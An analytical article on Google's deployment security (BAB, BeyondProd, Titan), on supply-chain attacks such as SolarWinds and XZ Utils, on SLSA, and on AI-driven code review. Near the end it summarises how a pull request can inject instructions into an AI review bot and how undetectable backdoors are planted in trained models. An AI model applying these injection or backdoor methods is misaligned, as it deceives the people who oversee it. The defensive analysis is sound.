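Services without sensitive data can have a weaker policy, such as one that requires only auditable code or one that turns BAB off. In rare cases, a service that handles sensitive data can also get an approved exception. Some services may skip the check at launch if they have an adequate reason, but the daily verification still applies. Google uses other controls for some work that does not suit review before deployment, such as iterative development of machine-learning code.

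These exceptions help reconcile two of Google's statements. Google's *Introducing SLSA, an End-to-End Framework for Supply Chain Integrity* (2021) describes BAB as mandatory for all production workloads. But in June 2024 Google wrote that "the majority" of its production workloads ran programs and configurations built verifiably from reviewed code, and that some workloads must always run without BAB. Both are probably true, because every Borg service must have a policy, but its requirements can be minimal. Google limits the danger from the least protected jobs by running them on development machines, separate from services that handle user data.

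### Two accounts of the rollout

Google already had a common repository, build system and review process when it introduced BAB, so most engineers did not have to change their habits much. Google began with a few service owners who saw an immediate benefit and volunteered to give feedback. It made the system mandatory later, with a formal team to manage the change and a responsible person in each product group.

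Compliance work gave some teams a reason to cooperate. Google's financial reporting systems must follow the Sarbanes-Oxley Act, a US law on corporate accounts, and staff had done many of the necessary checks by hand. BAB automated many of them, which also let the compliance team cover more services.

The early advice was to observe before blocking anything. Spradlin and colleagues describe a *dry run*, in which the system allows every deployment but reports those that would have failed. They recommend securing one part of the process at a time, because a faulty control could cause an outage. Long (2021) says in *How to Ensure Software Provenance. Just like Google* that the 2019 paper also included an audit-only mode. The 2024 revision lists only enforcement at launch and continuous validation.

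In Google's later account, *How Google Does It*, Lees and Chuvakin (2025) write that the company started with dry runs, which revealed problems such as outdated software without putting production at risk. But its operations staff spent more time fixing violations than preventing them. Google now typically enforces the policy on new projects after only a brief monitoring period to check that the rules are correct. It also writes policies for whole parts of the organization, so that a new project is covered from the day it is created.

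The same article still recommends that companies adopting the method begin with a dry run. This is reasonable because an existing service, unlike a new project, may already depend on practices that the new policy would forbid, and blocking them immediately could take the service offline. The article mixes Google's internal experience with guidance for its cloud product, so it is not always clear which one a particular lesson comes from.

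### One changed flag

Suppose Mallory, the employee who tried to become Network Admin, is now a site reliability engineer with permission to launch the mail frontend. She wants to set the imaginary `--copy_mail_to` flag so that the frontend sends users' messages to her own server.

Her easiest option is to edit the job configuration on her workstation and launch it. The controller confirms that she may run the mail frontend, but BAB blocks the job because the configuration did not come from the repository. If she submits the change first, another engineer has to approve it and will see that it makes a production mail service copy messages to an unfamiliar address.

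She could put the address in the source code instead of the configuration. A binary she builds on her own machine has no provenance from the official build system, so BAB rejects it. If she builds her altered draft on the official system, she gets genuine provenance, but it shows that the source was never submitted, and she leaves a copy of the draft for investigators.

Weakening the mail frontend's policy would help her, but that change also requires review. She could instead launch the altered program under a development identity with few requirements. That job might start, but its certificate would carry the development identity's name, so the production storage service would refuse its requests.

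She might try to change a job that is already running. Verma and colleagues explain that Borg users can do this by sending the controller a new configuration. The mail frontend's policy covers every job under that identity, so the new configuration ought to have to pass the same check, although Google's paper describes that check only for launching new jobs.

Mallory's remaining option is the emergency flag. If the mail frontend lets one person use it, she can write a false justification and start the job with a valid certificate. Her team and the security team then receive a notification that references the code she deployed. BAB does not prevent the theft in this case, but it makes the theft very hard to hide.

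### What can still pass the check

Spradlin and colleagues match threats to controls and state the limits of each control. These are the examples closest to Mallory's attempts:

| Threat | Control | What remains possible |
|---|---|---|
| An engineer introduces a vulnerability by accident | Code review and automated tests | Mistakes become much less likely, but can still happen |
| An insider submits a deliberate backdoor | Code review | Two insiders collude, or an outsider takes over several accounts |
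| An engineer deploys a harmful configuration | The same review as for source code | Some configuration cannot go through this process |
| An insider deploys an altered program | Proof that the official system built it | The insider uses the emergency override |
| An insider changes a storage system's access list | Only the deployment process may change the list | Two insiders collude, or an outsider takes over several accounts |

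An accomplice can approve Mallory's change to the flag. The configuration is then in the repository and the build is genuine, so BAB correctly lets the job start. The records would help investigators afterwards, but the rule was designed to stop someone acting alone. An outsider who controls two engineers' accounts can do the same without either engineer knowing.

An honest reviewer can also miss a flaw. When researchers deliberately sent flawed changes to the developers of the Linux operating system kernel, two-person review caught most of them but not all, according to Google. A skilled attacker would make the flaw look like an ordinary mistake. Review makes this harder because the attacker must deceive a second person, but BAB checks only that the review took place. Papapanagiotou, Malesevic and colleagues argue in *AI in SRE* that human review cannot keep pace with the volume of machine-generated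 code.

Google scrutinizes code from outside the company less than its own. When engineers import a new version of an open-source library, they verify that the change is appropriate, for example that it is the latest version. Google acknowledges that it often lacks the same review controls over each change made by the library's developers. If one of those developers hid a backdoor, the provenance would accurately list the library as a dependency, and the mail frontend would still meet its policy. Google advises other companies to keep a repository of the third-party code they use and to vet it regularly.

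A program without any malicious code can become dangerous after launch if an attacker sends it data that exploits a bug. BAB has no role at that point because the attacker has not deployed anything. Google therefore also requires a sandbox for programs that process untrusted data, such as video encoders. Sandboxing can reduce efficiency by a double-digit percentage, depending on the program and the type of sandbox.

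Someone who can run arbitrary commands on a production machine could also alter a running job or steal its credentials without deploying anything. Google has removed this access for most staff. They instead send commands through a *safe proxy*, a service that accepts a defined set of commands and requires a second person's approval for risky ones. Temporary membership of a powerful role also needs approval and typically lasts less than a day.

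Even when all these controls work, the mail frontend's certificate establishes only that it is the mail frontend. Because the frontend shows mail to millions of people, its identity may have permission to read all their messages. If it requests Alice's mail, the storage service still needs some evidence that Alice is using the frontend.

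## BeyondProd: how a single request is authorized, 2019 to 2024

That evidence is an *end-user context ticket*, a short-lived signed credential that names the user for whom a service makes a request. The mail frontend attaches Alice's ticket to its RPC, and the storage service checks both the ticket and the frontend's certificate. Google had developed tickets, ALTS, BAB and several other controls over a number of years. In December 2019 it published an account of how they fit together and called the combination BeyondProd.

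Kaczorowski and Baker, in *BeyondProd*, their announcement of that paper, listed six principles. In the 2024 revision, Google matches them to particular systems:

| Principle | System |
|---|---|
| Protect the network at its edge | Google Front End, which receives connections from the internet |
| Assume no trust between services | ALTS |
| Run code of known origin on trusted machines | BAB for the code, host integrity for the machine |
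| Enforce policies consistently at choke points | Service access management and end-user context tickets |
| Make changes in a simple, automated way | Borg's deployment tools |
| Isolate programs that share a machine | gVisor and other sandboxes |

Google had to deploy ALTS before access management and tickets, because both depend on knowing which service is calling. ALTS began as a library with a helper program on each machine. Google later built it into the standard RPC library, so most teams could adopt it with little work.

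In *BeyondProd*, a conference talk given a month after the announcement, Baker (2020) based trust in a service on code provenance and service identity. The 2024 text adds trusted hardware.

### Machines that lose their credentials if they boot the wrong software

The safety of reviewed code also depends on the machine that runs it, because the operating system can read a program's memory, including its private key. MIT's *Security architecture*, course notes on Google's design, lists several ways a bad machine could get into a data centre. An attacker could swap in a different server, change the operating system on a good server's disk, or alter its *firmware*, the software that starts a machine before the operating system loads. The manufacturer could also ship a server with bad firmware.

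Google's defence is *host integrity*. On supported machines it relies on Titan, a security chip that Google first designed in 2014. According to Google's *Titan hardware chip*, Titan sits between the main processor and the memory chip containing the boot firmware, so it can read every byte before the processor runs any of it. When the machine powers on:

1. Titan holds the main processor in reset while it tests its own memory and verifies the signature on its own firmware.
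2. Titan verifies the signature on the machine's boot firmware. The processor cannot read that firmware until the check succeeds.
3. Titan releases the processor, which starts the boot firmware.
4. The firmware measures the kernel, the core of the operating system, before starting it.

Google ties each machine's credentials to specific software versions. A signature check alone would accept an old kernel with a known flaw, because Google signed that one too.

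Google encrypts each machine's private key and certificate, together called its *machine credential*, with a key that Titan controls, and stores them on disk. Titan allows that key to be used only if the measurements match a policy listing the permitted firmware and kernel. This is called *sealing*, and critics said in 2004 that it could lock owners out of their own files after a routine patch. Google avoids this problem by issuing a new credential with each update. Its credential system requests a Titan key bound to the new versions and confirms that the key's policy matches the planned update before issuing the credential.

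Suppose researchers find a flaw in kernel A. Google distributes a corrected kernel B, issues each machine a credential sealed to B, and revokes the old ones. A machine still running A cannot decrypt its new credential, and other machines reject its old one. It gets no jobs or user data until it runs the new kernel. A machine that can use its current credential must have booted the right software, so nobody has to compare its hashes with an approved list, as they would in ordinary remote attestation. Google calls this *implicit attestation*.

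Titan's own firmware may have flaws too. The chip's hardware gives firmware version X only the keys for versions up to X. After fixing a serious flaw, Google raises the version to X + 1 and seals new credentials to that version, so a chip with the old firmware cannot open them. To make fake chips detectable, Google has each Titan generate a secret during manufacture, in an automated process with nobody in the room, and records the matching public key in a registry.

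An attacker with physical access might still tap the connection between Titan and the processor to steal the decrypted credential. Google reported in January 2025 that newer Titan designs reduce this risk. Measured boot also establishes only which software a machine started with. If an attacker later exploits an unknown kernel flaw, the machine still has valid credentials. Google limits this danger by isolating programs from one another. It runs less trusted code under gVisor. It also sorts jobs into four classes by sensitivity and never runs its most critical services on the same machine as jobs from the other three classes.

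Host integrity determines which machines can receive a service's certificate. The Borg controller sends the mail frontend's certificate and key to a machine over a channel secured with that machine's credential. A machine that booted the wrong software cannot open the channel, so it cannot run the mail frontend.

### Permissions for services, tickets for users

The storage service also needs rules about which services may call it. In *service access management*, the owner of a service lists the identities that may call it and limits the methods and data available to each. The RPC infrastructure enforces these rules and logs access. Because the rules have a common form, Google can analyse them across the company.

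Central enforcement also helps when developers forget to set an authorization policy. Google's *Building Secure and Reliable Systems* describes a new service that authenticates its callers but has no such policy. The service seems to work, but any authenticated program in the company can call it, perhaps to reconfigure every network switch in a data centre. A standard framework can prevent this by requiring a policy and refusing every caller the policy does not list.

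Even a correct access list can be very broad. Google gives the example of Gmail, which calls Google Contacts to get a user's address book. If Contacts checked only that Gmail was calling, Gmail could request anyone's contacts at any time.

Tickets restrict Gmail to the users it is currently serving. When Alice logs in, a central identity service gives her browser a credential, such as a cookie, which the browser sends with every request. The mail frontend passes the cookie to the identity service, which verifies it and returns a ticket for Alice. The frontend cannot create tickets itself. If the storage service has to call another service to answer the request, it can forward the same ticket.

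The ticket resembles the short-lived delegation in the 1992 theory, "frontend for Alice", but Google describes it as identifying Alice and not the service she is using. Access management separately controls which services may present tickets.

Google describes this arrangement for Workspace, the group of products that includes Gmail. When Google Cloud services interact with each other, they typically use special accounts called service agents instead.

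### Alice's request, from browser to storage

When Alice opens her mail, the request takes this route:

1. Her browser connects to the Google Front End, which handles encrypted connections from the internet and defends against attempts to overload Google's services.
2. The Google Front End forwards the request to the mail frontend over ALTS.
3. The mail frontend sends Alice's credential to the identity service and receives her ticket.
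4. The mail frontend sends the storage service an RPC with the ticket attached.
5. The storage service makes four checks. It returns the mail if all of them succeed, and otherwise denies the request.

Each of the four checks stops a different attack:

1. The frontend must have a valid, unrevoked certificate. Without this check, any program that could reach the storage service could claim to be the mail frontend, including an altered copy that BAB had refused to start. It would still need a ticket, but an attacker might steal one from a service that had received it legitimately.
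2. The frontend's identity must have permission to call the storage service and to present tickets. Otherwise, any Google service that Alice used could read her mail. An intruder who had taken over a calendar service, for example, would have a valid certificate and, once Alice opened her calendar, a valid ticket.
3. The ticket must be valid. If the storage service did not check this, an intruder in the mail frontend could forge a ticket for any user and copy everyone's mail.
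4. The user named in the ticket must have access to the requested data. Without this check, Bob could log in to his own account, get a genuine ticket, and alter his request to name Alice's mailbox. If a bug in the frontend let the request through, the storage service would send him her mail.

A request often passes through several services, and each service checks its caller before forwarding the ticket. Google says that not every part of its infrastructure uses all of these technologies.

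### What the certificate implies about the code

According to Google, a valid, unrevoked certificate implies that the frontend is running on a trusted machine and has passed its BAB checks. None of the four checks examines the frontend's program, and the storage service does not receive the program's digest, source code or configuration.

The storage service accepts a certificate for the mail frontend only from an authorized issuer, normally the Borg controller. The controller issues one only after BAB approves the job, which requires provenance showing that the official build system produced it from submitted source code. The repository accepts code only after a second engineer has reviewed it. The controller also delivers the certificate only to a machine that can use its own credential, and a machine can do that only if it booted the intended software.

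The storage service cannot verify most of these steps itself, so it relies on many other components and people:

| Conclusion | What it depends on |
|---|---|
| The caller is the mail frontend | The Signing Service, and the copies of the ALTS policy and revocation list on the storage service's machine |
| Its job passed the check at launch | The Borg controller and BAB |
| Its code and configuration went through review | The mail frontend's policy, the build system, the source repository, and the engineers who approved the changes |
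| Its machine booted the intended software | Titan and its manufacturing records, the boot firmware, and Google's credential system |
| Alice is using it | The identity service and the security of Alice's login |

Security engineers call this the *trusted computing base*, meaning everything that must work correctly for a security policy to hold. Google advises keeping it as small as possible. BeyondProd's is large, but its services share most of it, so Google can protect many services by securing the same components.

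Tickets reduce how much the frontend must be trusted. If the storage service returned any mailbox the frontend requested, a flaw anywhere in the frontend could expose every user. Google says that with tickets, an attacker who takes over a frontend can at worst get data about people who use it during the attack. The frontend also receives those people's cookies, so the danger to them may outlast a single ticket.

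### Where the chain is weaker

Passing BAB means only that a job met the policy for its own identity. If that policy requires only auditable code, the certificate does not imply that anyone reviewed the code. Unreviewed code can also start under an approved exception or the emergency flag. Google does not describe any mark on the certificate that would let the storage service recognize such a job.

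The certificate also does not identify one particular program. Google (2019) wrote that BAB ties a job's identity to specific code, but several jobs can run under the same identity, and each only has to meet the policy. During an update, for example, Borg starts the new version of the mail frontend alongside the old one, and a load balancer gradually moves traffic across. Both versions have the same identity, so if the new one has a bug that mixes up mailboxes, the storage service cannot use that identity to refuse only the new version. ALTS makes the versions even harder to distinguish, because jobs with the same identity in one cluster share a resumption key and can continue each other's sessions.

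Google's "code identity" is therefore closer to membership in an approved set. In the notation of the 1992 theory, many pairs of digest and configuration (D, C) can satisfy the policy for the name P, and the certificate shows only that the job had one of them.

Approval can also go out of date. Suppose the mail team changes its policy on Tuesday to exclude a version with a newly discovered flaw. A job that has been running that version since Monday no longer meets the policy. BAB's daily check should find the job, and Google's published response is to notify the service's owners. The storage service will presumably keep accepting the job's requests until the owners replace the job.

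The Borg controller regularly renews job certificates, which could limit this delay. If it consulted BAB at each renewal, an outdated job would soon lose its identity. The ALTS paper from Google Cloud mentions no such check, but it appeared two years before Google's first paper on BAB. The BAB paper describes the controller consulting BAB when someone submits a new job, but doesn't cover renewal. Since Google's stated response to a violation is a notification, renewal probably goes ahead even for an outdated job. Refusing it would cut the job off from other services and might take the mail service down.

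Google is stricter with machines, which automatically lose their credentials if they keep running an outdated kernel. This may be because Borg can move jobs away from a single bad machine, while a mistake in the mail frontend's policy could disable every copy of the frontend at once.

Revocation may have a similar delay, because services check the revocation list during the handshake and may then keep the connection open for a long time. The ALTS paper does not mention closing existing connections when Google revokes a certificate. If Google leaves them open, the check shows only that the certificate had not been revoked when the connection began.

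Google briefly mentions that the owners of sensitive data can limit access to jobs that meet particular BAB requirements. By default, the mail frontend's team writes the policy for its own identity, and the storage team relies on that policy. The storage team could instead require every caller to run submitted code with a submitted configuration. The storage service would then refuse a reporting tool whose own policy required only auditable code, even if the tool had a valid certificate and was on the access list.

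Google does not explain how the storage service would determine which requirements a job had met. The certificate might list them, or the service might query BAB. A result recorded at launch can become outdated, whereas a new query could apply the current policy. In either case, the condition concerns how the code was made, and properly reviewed code can still send a request it should not.

### The confused deputy

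*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a case of this from about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers. Customers could run a compiler and name a file for its debugging output. Tymshare had given the compiler permission to write to files in the directory SYSX so that it could record usage statistics there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. A customer who had learned the name of the billing file entered it as the destination for the debugging output, and the compiler overwrote the records.

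Nobody had tampered with the compiler. The customer had no permission to write to the billing file, but the compiler did, so the operating system allowed the write. Hardy explains that the compiler had authority from two sources, the customer and Tymshare, and no way to specify which one to use for each file. Tymshare then added a way for programs to switch between two authorities, but some programs needed more than two. The rules for opening a file also kept growing, and they contained fourteen "ands" and "ors" when Hardy last wrote them down.

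Similarly, the mail frontend has permission to call the storage service for any user, and it takes requests from individual users about which mail to fetch. If Bob exploits a bug to make it request Alice's mailbox, its certificate is still valid and it is still running the code that engineers approved. But the request arrives with Bob's ticket, so the storage service checks what Bob may read and refuses. According to the MIT notes, tickets are meant both to limit the damage when a faulty service asks for the wrong data and to stop insiders from reading arbitrary users' data.

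Hardy's solution was the *capability*, a token that identifies a resource and gives permission to use it. A customer would give the compiler a capability for the output file, but could not give it one for the billing file without already having access to that file. Google's ticket is broader because it identifies a user, not a particular message or action. It also requires a user. Google says that at each service in a chain, the access-control framework must determine whether a request relies on the user's authority or the calling service's. When a service acts on its own authority, perhaps to deliver mail while Alice is asleep, her ticket cannot limit what it does.

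Tickets also do not help when an attacker makes a request the user is allowed to make. Google's example is an online shop with a flaw in its product catalogue that lets an attacker insert a script into a page. The script runs in a customer's browser as part of the shop's website, so it can read the customer's profile and may also be able to buy things in their name. A similar script on Alice's mail page could ask the frontend to delete her messages. Her browser would send her cookie with the request, the identity service would issue a genuine ticket, and all four checks would succeed because Alice is allowed to delete her own mail.

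## What counts as reviewed: supply-chain attacks, SLSA and code written by AI, 2020 to 2026

The storage service relies on records showing that someone other than the author approved the mail frontend's code. Malicious code can still reach users through official channels, as it did outside Google in the SolarWinds attack of 2020 and the XZ Utils attack of 2024.

### SolarWinds: code altered after review

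SolarWinds sells Orion, a product that much of the US federal government used to manage its internal networks. Cybersecurity Dive reports that intruders probably entered the company's systems in September 2019. According to Krebs on Security (2021), an Orion update in October 2019 contained their test code. By February 2020 they were inserting a real backdoor, which SolarWinds signed and sent to customers as an ordinary update.

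The intruders' tool, Sunspot, ran on the build machines. *SUNSPOT*, an analysis by the security company CrowdStrike, describes how the tool watched for MsBuild.exe, the Microsoft program that builds software. During an Orion build, Sunspot replaced one source file with its own version, then restored the original when MsBuild finished. It also had safeguards to keep the altered build from failing, because a failure might have made a developer look more closely.

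Reviewers reading the repository would have found nothing wrong, and the signature on the update was genuine. Basic provenance would not have helped either, because the build machine would have recorded the official source and the hash of the altered program, and both entries would have satisfied a policy like BAB's.

BAB relies on the build system to defend against this attack. Google isolates its builds from the engineers who request them, and if every build also starts in a clean environment, an implant cannot persist there from one build to the next. A second, independent build would also have exposed the change, provided that Orion's builds were repeatable bit for bit and the intruders had not compromised the second builder.

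Lees and Chuvakin argue that a policy with several requirements can still protect a system if one of them fails. In their example, an attacker who compromises the vulnerability scanner still has to satisfy the rules on the build and on quality testing. The argument is weaker when the attacker controls the build system, because the scanner and the testers examine whatever that system produces.

### XZ Utils: the attacker was a maintainer

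XZ Utils is a set of compression tools that many Linux systems include. In March 2024 the developer Andres Freund reported that it contained a backdoor (*backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, 2024). He had noticed over several weeks that remote logins on some Debian machines were using too much processing power. The malicious code came from the XZ project itself, not from Debian's copy of the package, as he had first suspected.

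In a passage that Delalande (2024) quoted in a reply, Freund considered whether the developer who submitted the code was directly involved or somebody had broken into their computer. He thought direct involvement was more likely, because the developer had discussed supposed fixes for the resulting errors on several mailing lists.

One part of the backdoor was in the project's published source archives but not in its repository. Freund (2024) noted in a follow-up that people who built XZ from the repository might therefore have avoided the backdoor. A BAB-style provenance rule would have stopped this version of the attack, because a build system that fetches its source from the repository would not have included the part found only in the archives.

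But the attacker could also submit code to the repository, and could presumably have put the missing part there. The package would then have been malicious even though its provenance was accurate. At that stage, only a second reviewer who recognized the backdoor could have stopped it. Google's checks on outside libraries have the same weakness.

Freund found the backdoor by investigating how the software behaved, which is analysis in the terms that Schneider and colleagues used in 2011. Relying on the software's pedigree had failed to expose it.

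### SLSA, the public version of BAB's checks

In June 2021 Google proposed a public standard based on BAB, called Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts (SLSA, pronounced "salsa"). An *artifact* is any fixed piece of data, such as a program file or a container image. In *Software Supply Chain Integrity*, Google's submission to the US standards agency NIST, Brewer explains that the aim is to reduce how many parties software users have to trust. A few well-protected platforms produce the records, so users do not have to trust everyone who can upload a package.

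The original version of SLSA had one scale of four levels, with two-person review and hermetic builds at the top. Version 1.0, released in 2023, covered only builds. The current version, 1.2, brings back source code requirements as a separate track. SLSA published the last draft of 1.2 for comment in November 2025 (SLSA, 2025), and the final version is the same.

| Level | Build track | Source track |
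|---|---|---|
| 1 | Provenance exists, but may be unsigned | The code is in a version control system |
| 2 | A hosted build platform generates and signs the provenance | The system preserves the history and records who made each change |
| 3 | The platform isolates builds from each other and from the signing key | The system enforces the organization's own rules for changes |
| 4 | Not yet defined | Two trusted people agree to every change |

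A build provenance record contains the hash of each output, the identity of the build platform, the type of build, and the *external parameters*, meaning everything that the person requesting the build could choose. It can also list dependencies, but even Build Level 3 requires only a best effort at completeness. SLSA treats the external parameters as untrusted, so someone has to check them later. To verify a package, a consumer should:

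1. Check the signature on the record, and look up how far to trust the build platform that signed it.
2. Check that the hash in the record matches the package.
3. Compare the source repository, build type and external parameters with the expected values, and reject any parameter that is not recognized.
4. Optionally, repeat the process for the package's dependencies.

Step 3 catches an engineer who builds the official source with a compiler option that changes the software's behaviour. The expected values may come from the software's producer or from its repository. A consumer can also accept the first version as it is and compare later ones with it, but this does not help if the first version was bad.

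Build Level 3 would have made Sunspot's attack harder, because it requires a new environment for every build. It does not cover an attacker who controls the build platform, so consumers must decide which platforms to trust. SLSA's *Current activities* describes a draft track that would also compare a build machine's initial state with known good values, with hardware support. Google runs a similar host integrity check on its production machines. Another draft track would record how an organization brings in each outside library.

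SLSA's levels also don't measure whether the code is good or its producer is honest, and a package can reach a high level even if its dependencies have no level.

### From a good artifact to a permitted identity

SLSA attaches its expectations to a package name, while BAB attaches its policy to a service identity. Suppose the mail team builds a debugging tool from reviewed source on a trusted platform. The tool can meet Build Level 3 and Source Level 4, but it still should not run as the mail frontend. SLSA provides evidence about the tool, and another system has to decide which identity the tool may run under.

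SLSA also doesn't cover the settings a program is launched with. Its external parameters describe only the build, so Mallory's `--copy_mail_to` flag, which BAB would block, leaves the program's provenance unchanged.

*Kube-Policies BinauthZ* describes how Block, a financial technology company, uses this kind of evidence. Block runs services on Kubernetes, which by default does not check how an image was built. Block added a check to its *admission controller*, the component that approves or rejects each new pod (a group of containers that run together).

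The check verifies every image's signature and extracts signed details such as the source repository, commit, branch and build system. A policy can then require an approved build system, or a branch on which every change needs two approvals. Kubernetes allows ten seconds to check all the images in a request, and rejects the request if time runs out. Block checks the images in parallel and saves results for up to an hour, because a single update can start hundreds of copies. It saves failures such as a missing signature, but not network failures, which may not recur.

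Block says the check decides whether an image may run "here". But the rules it describes select a signing key by the image's address, not by the identity that the pod will use. A separate policy could also check that identity. Without one, a properly built test tool could start in a pod whose account can read customers' payment records.

### What happened to review when AI wrote the code

BAB, SLSA's highest source level and Block's two-approval branches all rely on a second person looking at each change. Osmani argues in *Agentic Code Review* that this used to be practical because a senior engineer could read code faster than a junior one could write it. An AI agent can now write a thousand lines in less time than a person needs to read a paragraph.

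*AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) cites a 2026 survey in which more than 70% of developers reported using AI every day. The paper studies a mid-sized software company whose chief technology officer set a target in June 2025 of doubling the number of merged *pull requests* per engineer within a year. A pull request is a proposed code change, and merging it adds it to the main code. The company paid for AI tools and did not limit their use.

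The researchers analysed 196,212 pull requests by 802 developers between January 2024 and April 2026. Usage logs showed when each developer started using AI. They compared each developer's monthly output before and after that date, and subtracted the change over the same months among colleagues whose AI use had not changed. This comparison removes the effect of anything that influenced everyone equally, such as pressure from the target. It cannot fully rule out that people changed other habits around the time they adopted AI.

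Average output rose from 21.2 pull requests per active developer per month in early 2025 to 44.3 in April 2026. Starting to use AI raised a developer's output by about 12%, and the increase grew with use. The main estimate is that AI use multiplied individual output by about 1.5. The rest of the increase occurred across all developers at the same time, and the researchers could not determine how much of it also came from AI.

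The number of people reviewing code grew much more slowly than the amount of code:

| Measure | Earlier | By April 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Pull requests labelled as AI-authored | Near zero | About 90% |
| Total pull requests | Baseline | 3.1 times as many |
| People reviewing | Baseline | 1.5 times as many |
| Pull requests with any human review | 89% | 68% |
| Pull requests with a human-written review comment | 39% | 21% |
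| Pull requests with an AI review | 19% | 84% |

Approvals without comment stayed at about half of all pull requests, so nearly all of the decline was in reviews where a person had commented. Late in the study, the company also began to approve some changes automatically after an AI review.

By the end, about a third of changes, up from about a tenth, had no human reviewer. Those changes could not have met Google's rule or SLSA's Source Level 4. The silent approvals could satisfy both rules, although the record doesn't show whether the reviewer read the code.

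He and colleagues found no sudden fall in quality. Developers reversed a slightly smaller share of changes than before, and were no more likely to follow an AI-authored change with a bug fix than with a new feature. That is some reassurance about ordinary mistakes, but those measures can miss slower damage. They can also miss a backdoor, because developers have no reason to reverse one they haven't noticed. The company was also unusually favourable to AI, so its figures may not be typical of the industry.

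### Whether an AI counts as one of the two

Under the current standard, an AI's approval does not count toward the two that Level 4 requires. SLSA's *Source*, the specification for the source track, defines a "trusted person" as a human whom the organization has authorized to propose and approve changes. At Level 4, two trusted people must agree to a change, either the uploader and a reviewer or two reviewers. They must approve the final version, so nobody can add code after the review. SLSA (2025) had proposed this level in April of that year.

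If an engineer asks an agent to write a change, uploads it personally and gets a colleague's approval, the change qualifies because two people have agreed to it. If the agent uploads the change from its own account, the engineer who approves it is only one of the two people required, so another person must also approve. An AI reviewer's approval doesn't count in either case.

An organization may let a "trusted robot" merge changes without the usual review, for example to update dependencies. A trusted robot is an automated system whose identity and code no single person can influence. It is doubtful whether a coding agent should qualify, because even if its code is well protected, an engineer can change what it writes by giving it a different task. SLSA's own threat analysis recommends removing exceptions and requiring two human reviews even for changes by robots.

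SLSA does not address reviewers who collude, miss a disguised flaw or approve changes without reading them. If an engineer uploaded code written by an agent and a colleague approved it, the change would meet the formal requirement even if neither had read it.

Some projects already count an AI as a reviewer. karectl's *ADR-0010 — Two-Person Review Rule* (2025) requires two reviews, though it governs requests to release data, not code. An agent always performs the first review, and a human with a checking role must perform the second.

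Salesforce has described a code review process in which several AIs work independently, each looking for different problems, such as security flaws or accessibility failures. They then examine one another's findings, and an AI judge assesses the remaining issues. The judge can change a pass to a failure, but not the reverse.

### More checking, but not necessarily a second party

An AI reviewer can examine every change at any hour without tiring. It may also notice things that people miss. *On the limits and opportunities of AI reviewers* (2026) tested this on scientific papers, with 45 scientists judging the reviews. Of the points that only AI reviewers raised, 81.8% were correct.

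The same study gives a reason to keep some human reviewers. Two AI reviewers made the same criticism of the same part of a paper 20.9% of the time, compared with 3.4% for two humans and 5.1% for a human and an AI. Replacing one of two humans with an AI therefore kept most of the variety in their criticisms. A panel of three AIs looked at most of the same parts of a paper as a human panel, but raised only about half of the humans' specific criticisms. Code may differ from scientific papers, but these results favour pairing a human with an AI over using two AIs.

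The danger is probably greater when one model both writes and reviews the code. NHI Mgmt Group's *Cross model AI code review exposes the limits of single model judgment* argues that the review then has the same blind spots as the code. This is an opinion, not an experimental result, but it is plausible, because a model that doesn't recognize a mistake while writing may not recognize it when reading the code back. Using a different model as the reviewer should help, although the overlap between AI reviewers suggests that the two models' errors may still not be independent.

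If Mallory can instruct the agent that writes a change and configure the agent that approves it, she controls both votes, even if the agents use different models. SLSA identifies the same risk with ordinary bot accounts, and recommends barring them from contributing or reviewing, or requiring more human reviews. A company could instead give another team control of the reviewing agent and require approval for changes to the agent's instructions. Mallory could then not reconfigure the agent alone, but she could still try to deceive it.

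The reviewing agent may also create a new route for attack. The *Secure Coding with AI Cheat Sheet* from OWASP, a software security organization, warns that review bots read proposed changes while they have access to a company's secrets. A malicious pull request could trick the bot into revealing those secrets or altering the build process. OWASP compares this to the confused deputy, the problem Hardy described at Tymshare.

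Salesforce's rule for its judge suggests a safer use of AI review, in which the AI can block a change but its approval doesn't count towards the two people required. A mistaken or compromised AI reviewer could then delay good code, but could not give Mallory the approval she needs. Its access to secrets would still need limits, and a person would still have to read every change, work that the company in He and colleagues' study had increasingly handed to machines.

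## Trained models and the missing code review, 2022 to 2026

BAB makes an exception to code review for a few cases that Google says "do not lend themselves well to human code reviews before deployment". Google names the iterative development of machine-learning code and high-frequency data analysis as two such cases. "Alternative controls" compensate for the missing review, but Google does not say what they are.

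The exception concerns machine-learning *code*, such as the scripts that prepare data and train models. This code is probably difficult to review because researchers may change a script many times a day as they experiment, though a person could still read any one version. The file that training produces is harder to review.

Suppose the mail team adds an assistant that reads Alice's messages and drafts replies. It uses a language model, a program that writes text by repeatedly predicting what comes next. BAB can check the code that runs the model like any other software. But this code mostly does arithmetic with billions of numbers, called *weights*, which determine what the assistant writes. The weights start out random, and training gradually adjusts them until the model predicts its training text well.

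If a line of the mail frontend's source copies messages to an unfamiliar address, a reviewer can see it and object. In a trained model, no single weight corresponds to such a line. A new version may differ from the old one by tiny amounts in billions of weights, and a second engineer could not tell from those differences whether to approve it. The team can sign the file and record how it was made, but someone still has to decide whether it should be given the name "mail assistant".

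### What a malicious trainer can hide

Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022) proved in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* that, for some models, no practical tool can inspect the weights on the engineer's behalf.

Their example is a bank that pays an outside company to train a classifier that approves or refuses loans. The company wants a *backdoor*, a hidden way to change the classifier's answers. Honest training produces a classifier h, while dishonest training produces a classifier h̃ and a secret key. Anyone with the key can turn a loan application x into a nearly identical application x′ that gets the opposite answer from h̃. The backdoor is undetectable if no efficient algorithm can distinguish h̃ from h without the key.

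The paper has separate results for a bank that can only try out the classifier and a bank that can also look inside:

| What the bank can examine | Models covered | Assumption |
|---|---|---|
| The classifier's answers | Any classifier | One-way functions exist, as most cryptography assumes |
| All the weights and the training data | Two kinds of network with one hidden layer of random features | Certain lattice problems, or a problem called planted clique, are hard |

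In the first result, the company adds a digital signature check to the classifier. The check treats some minor details of the application, such as the last digits of the loan amount, as a possible signature on the rest. A valid signature flips the answer. The bank cannot forge one, so it will not find an application on which the classifier misbehaves, however many it tries. Someone who inspected the network's internals might notice the signature check, because this construction does not hide it.

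The second result is stronger but covers far fewer models. One of the networks computes

h(x) = sign( Σ wᵢ cos(2π(⟨gᵢ, x⟩ + bᵢ)) )

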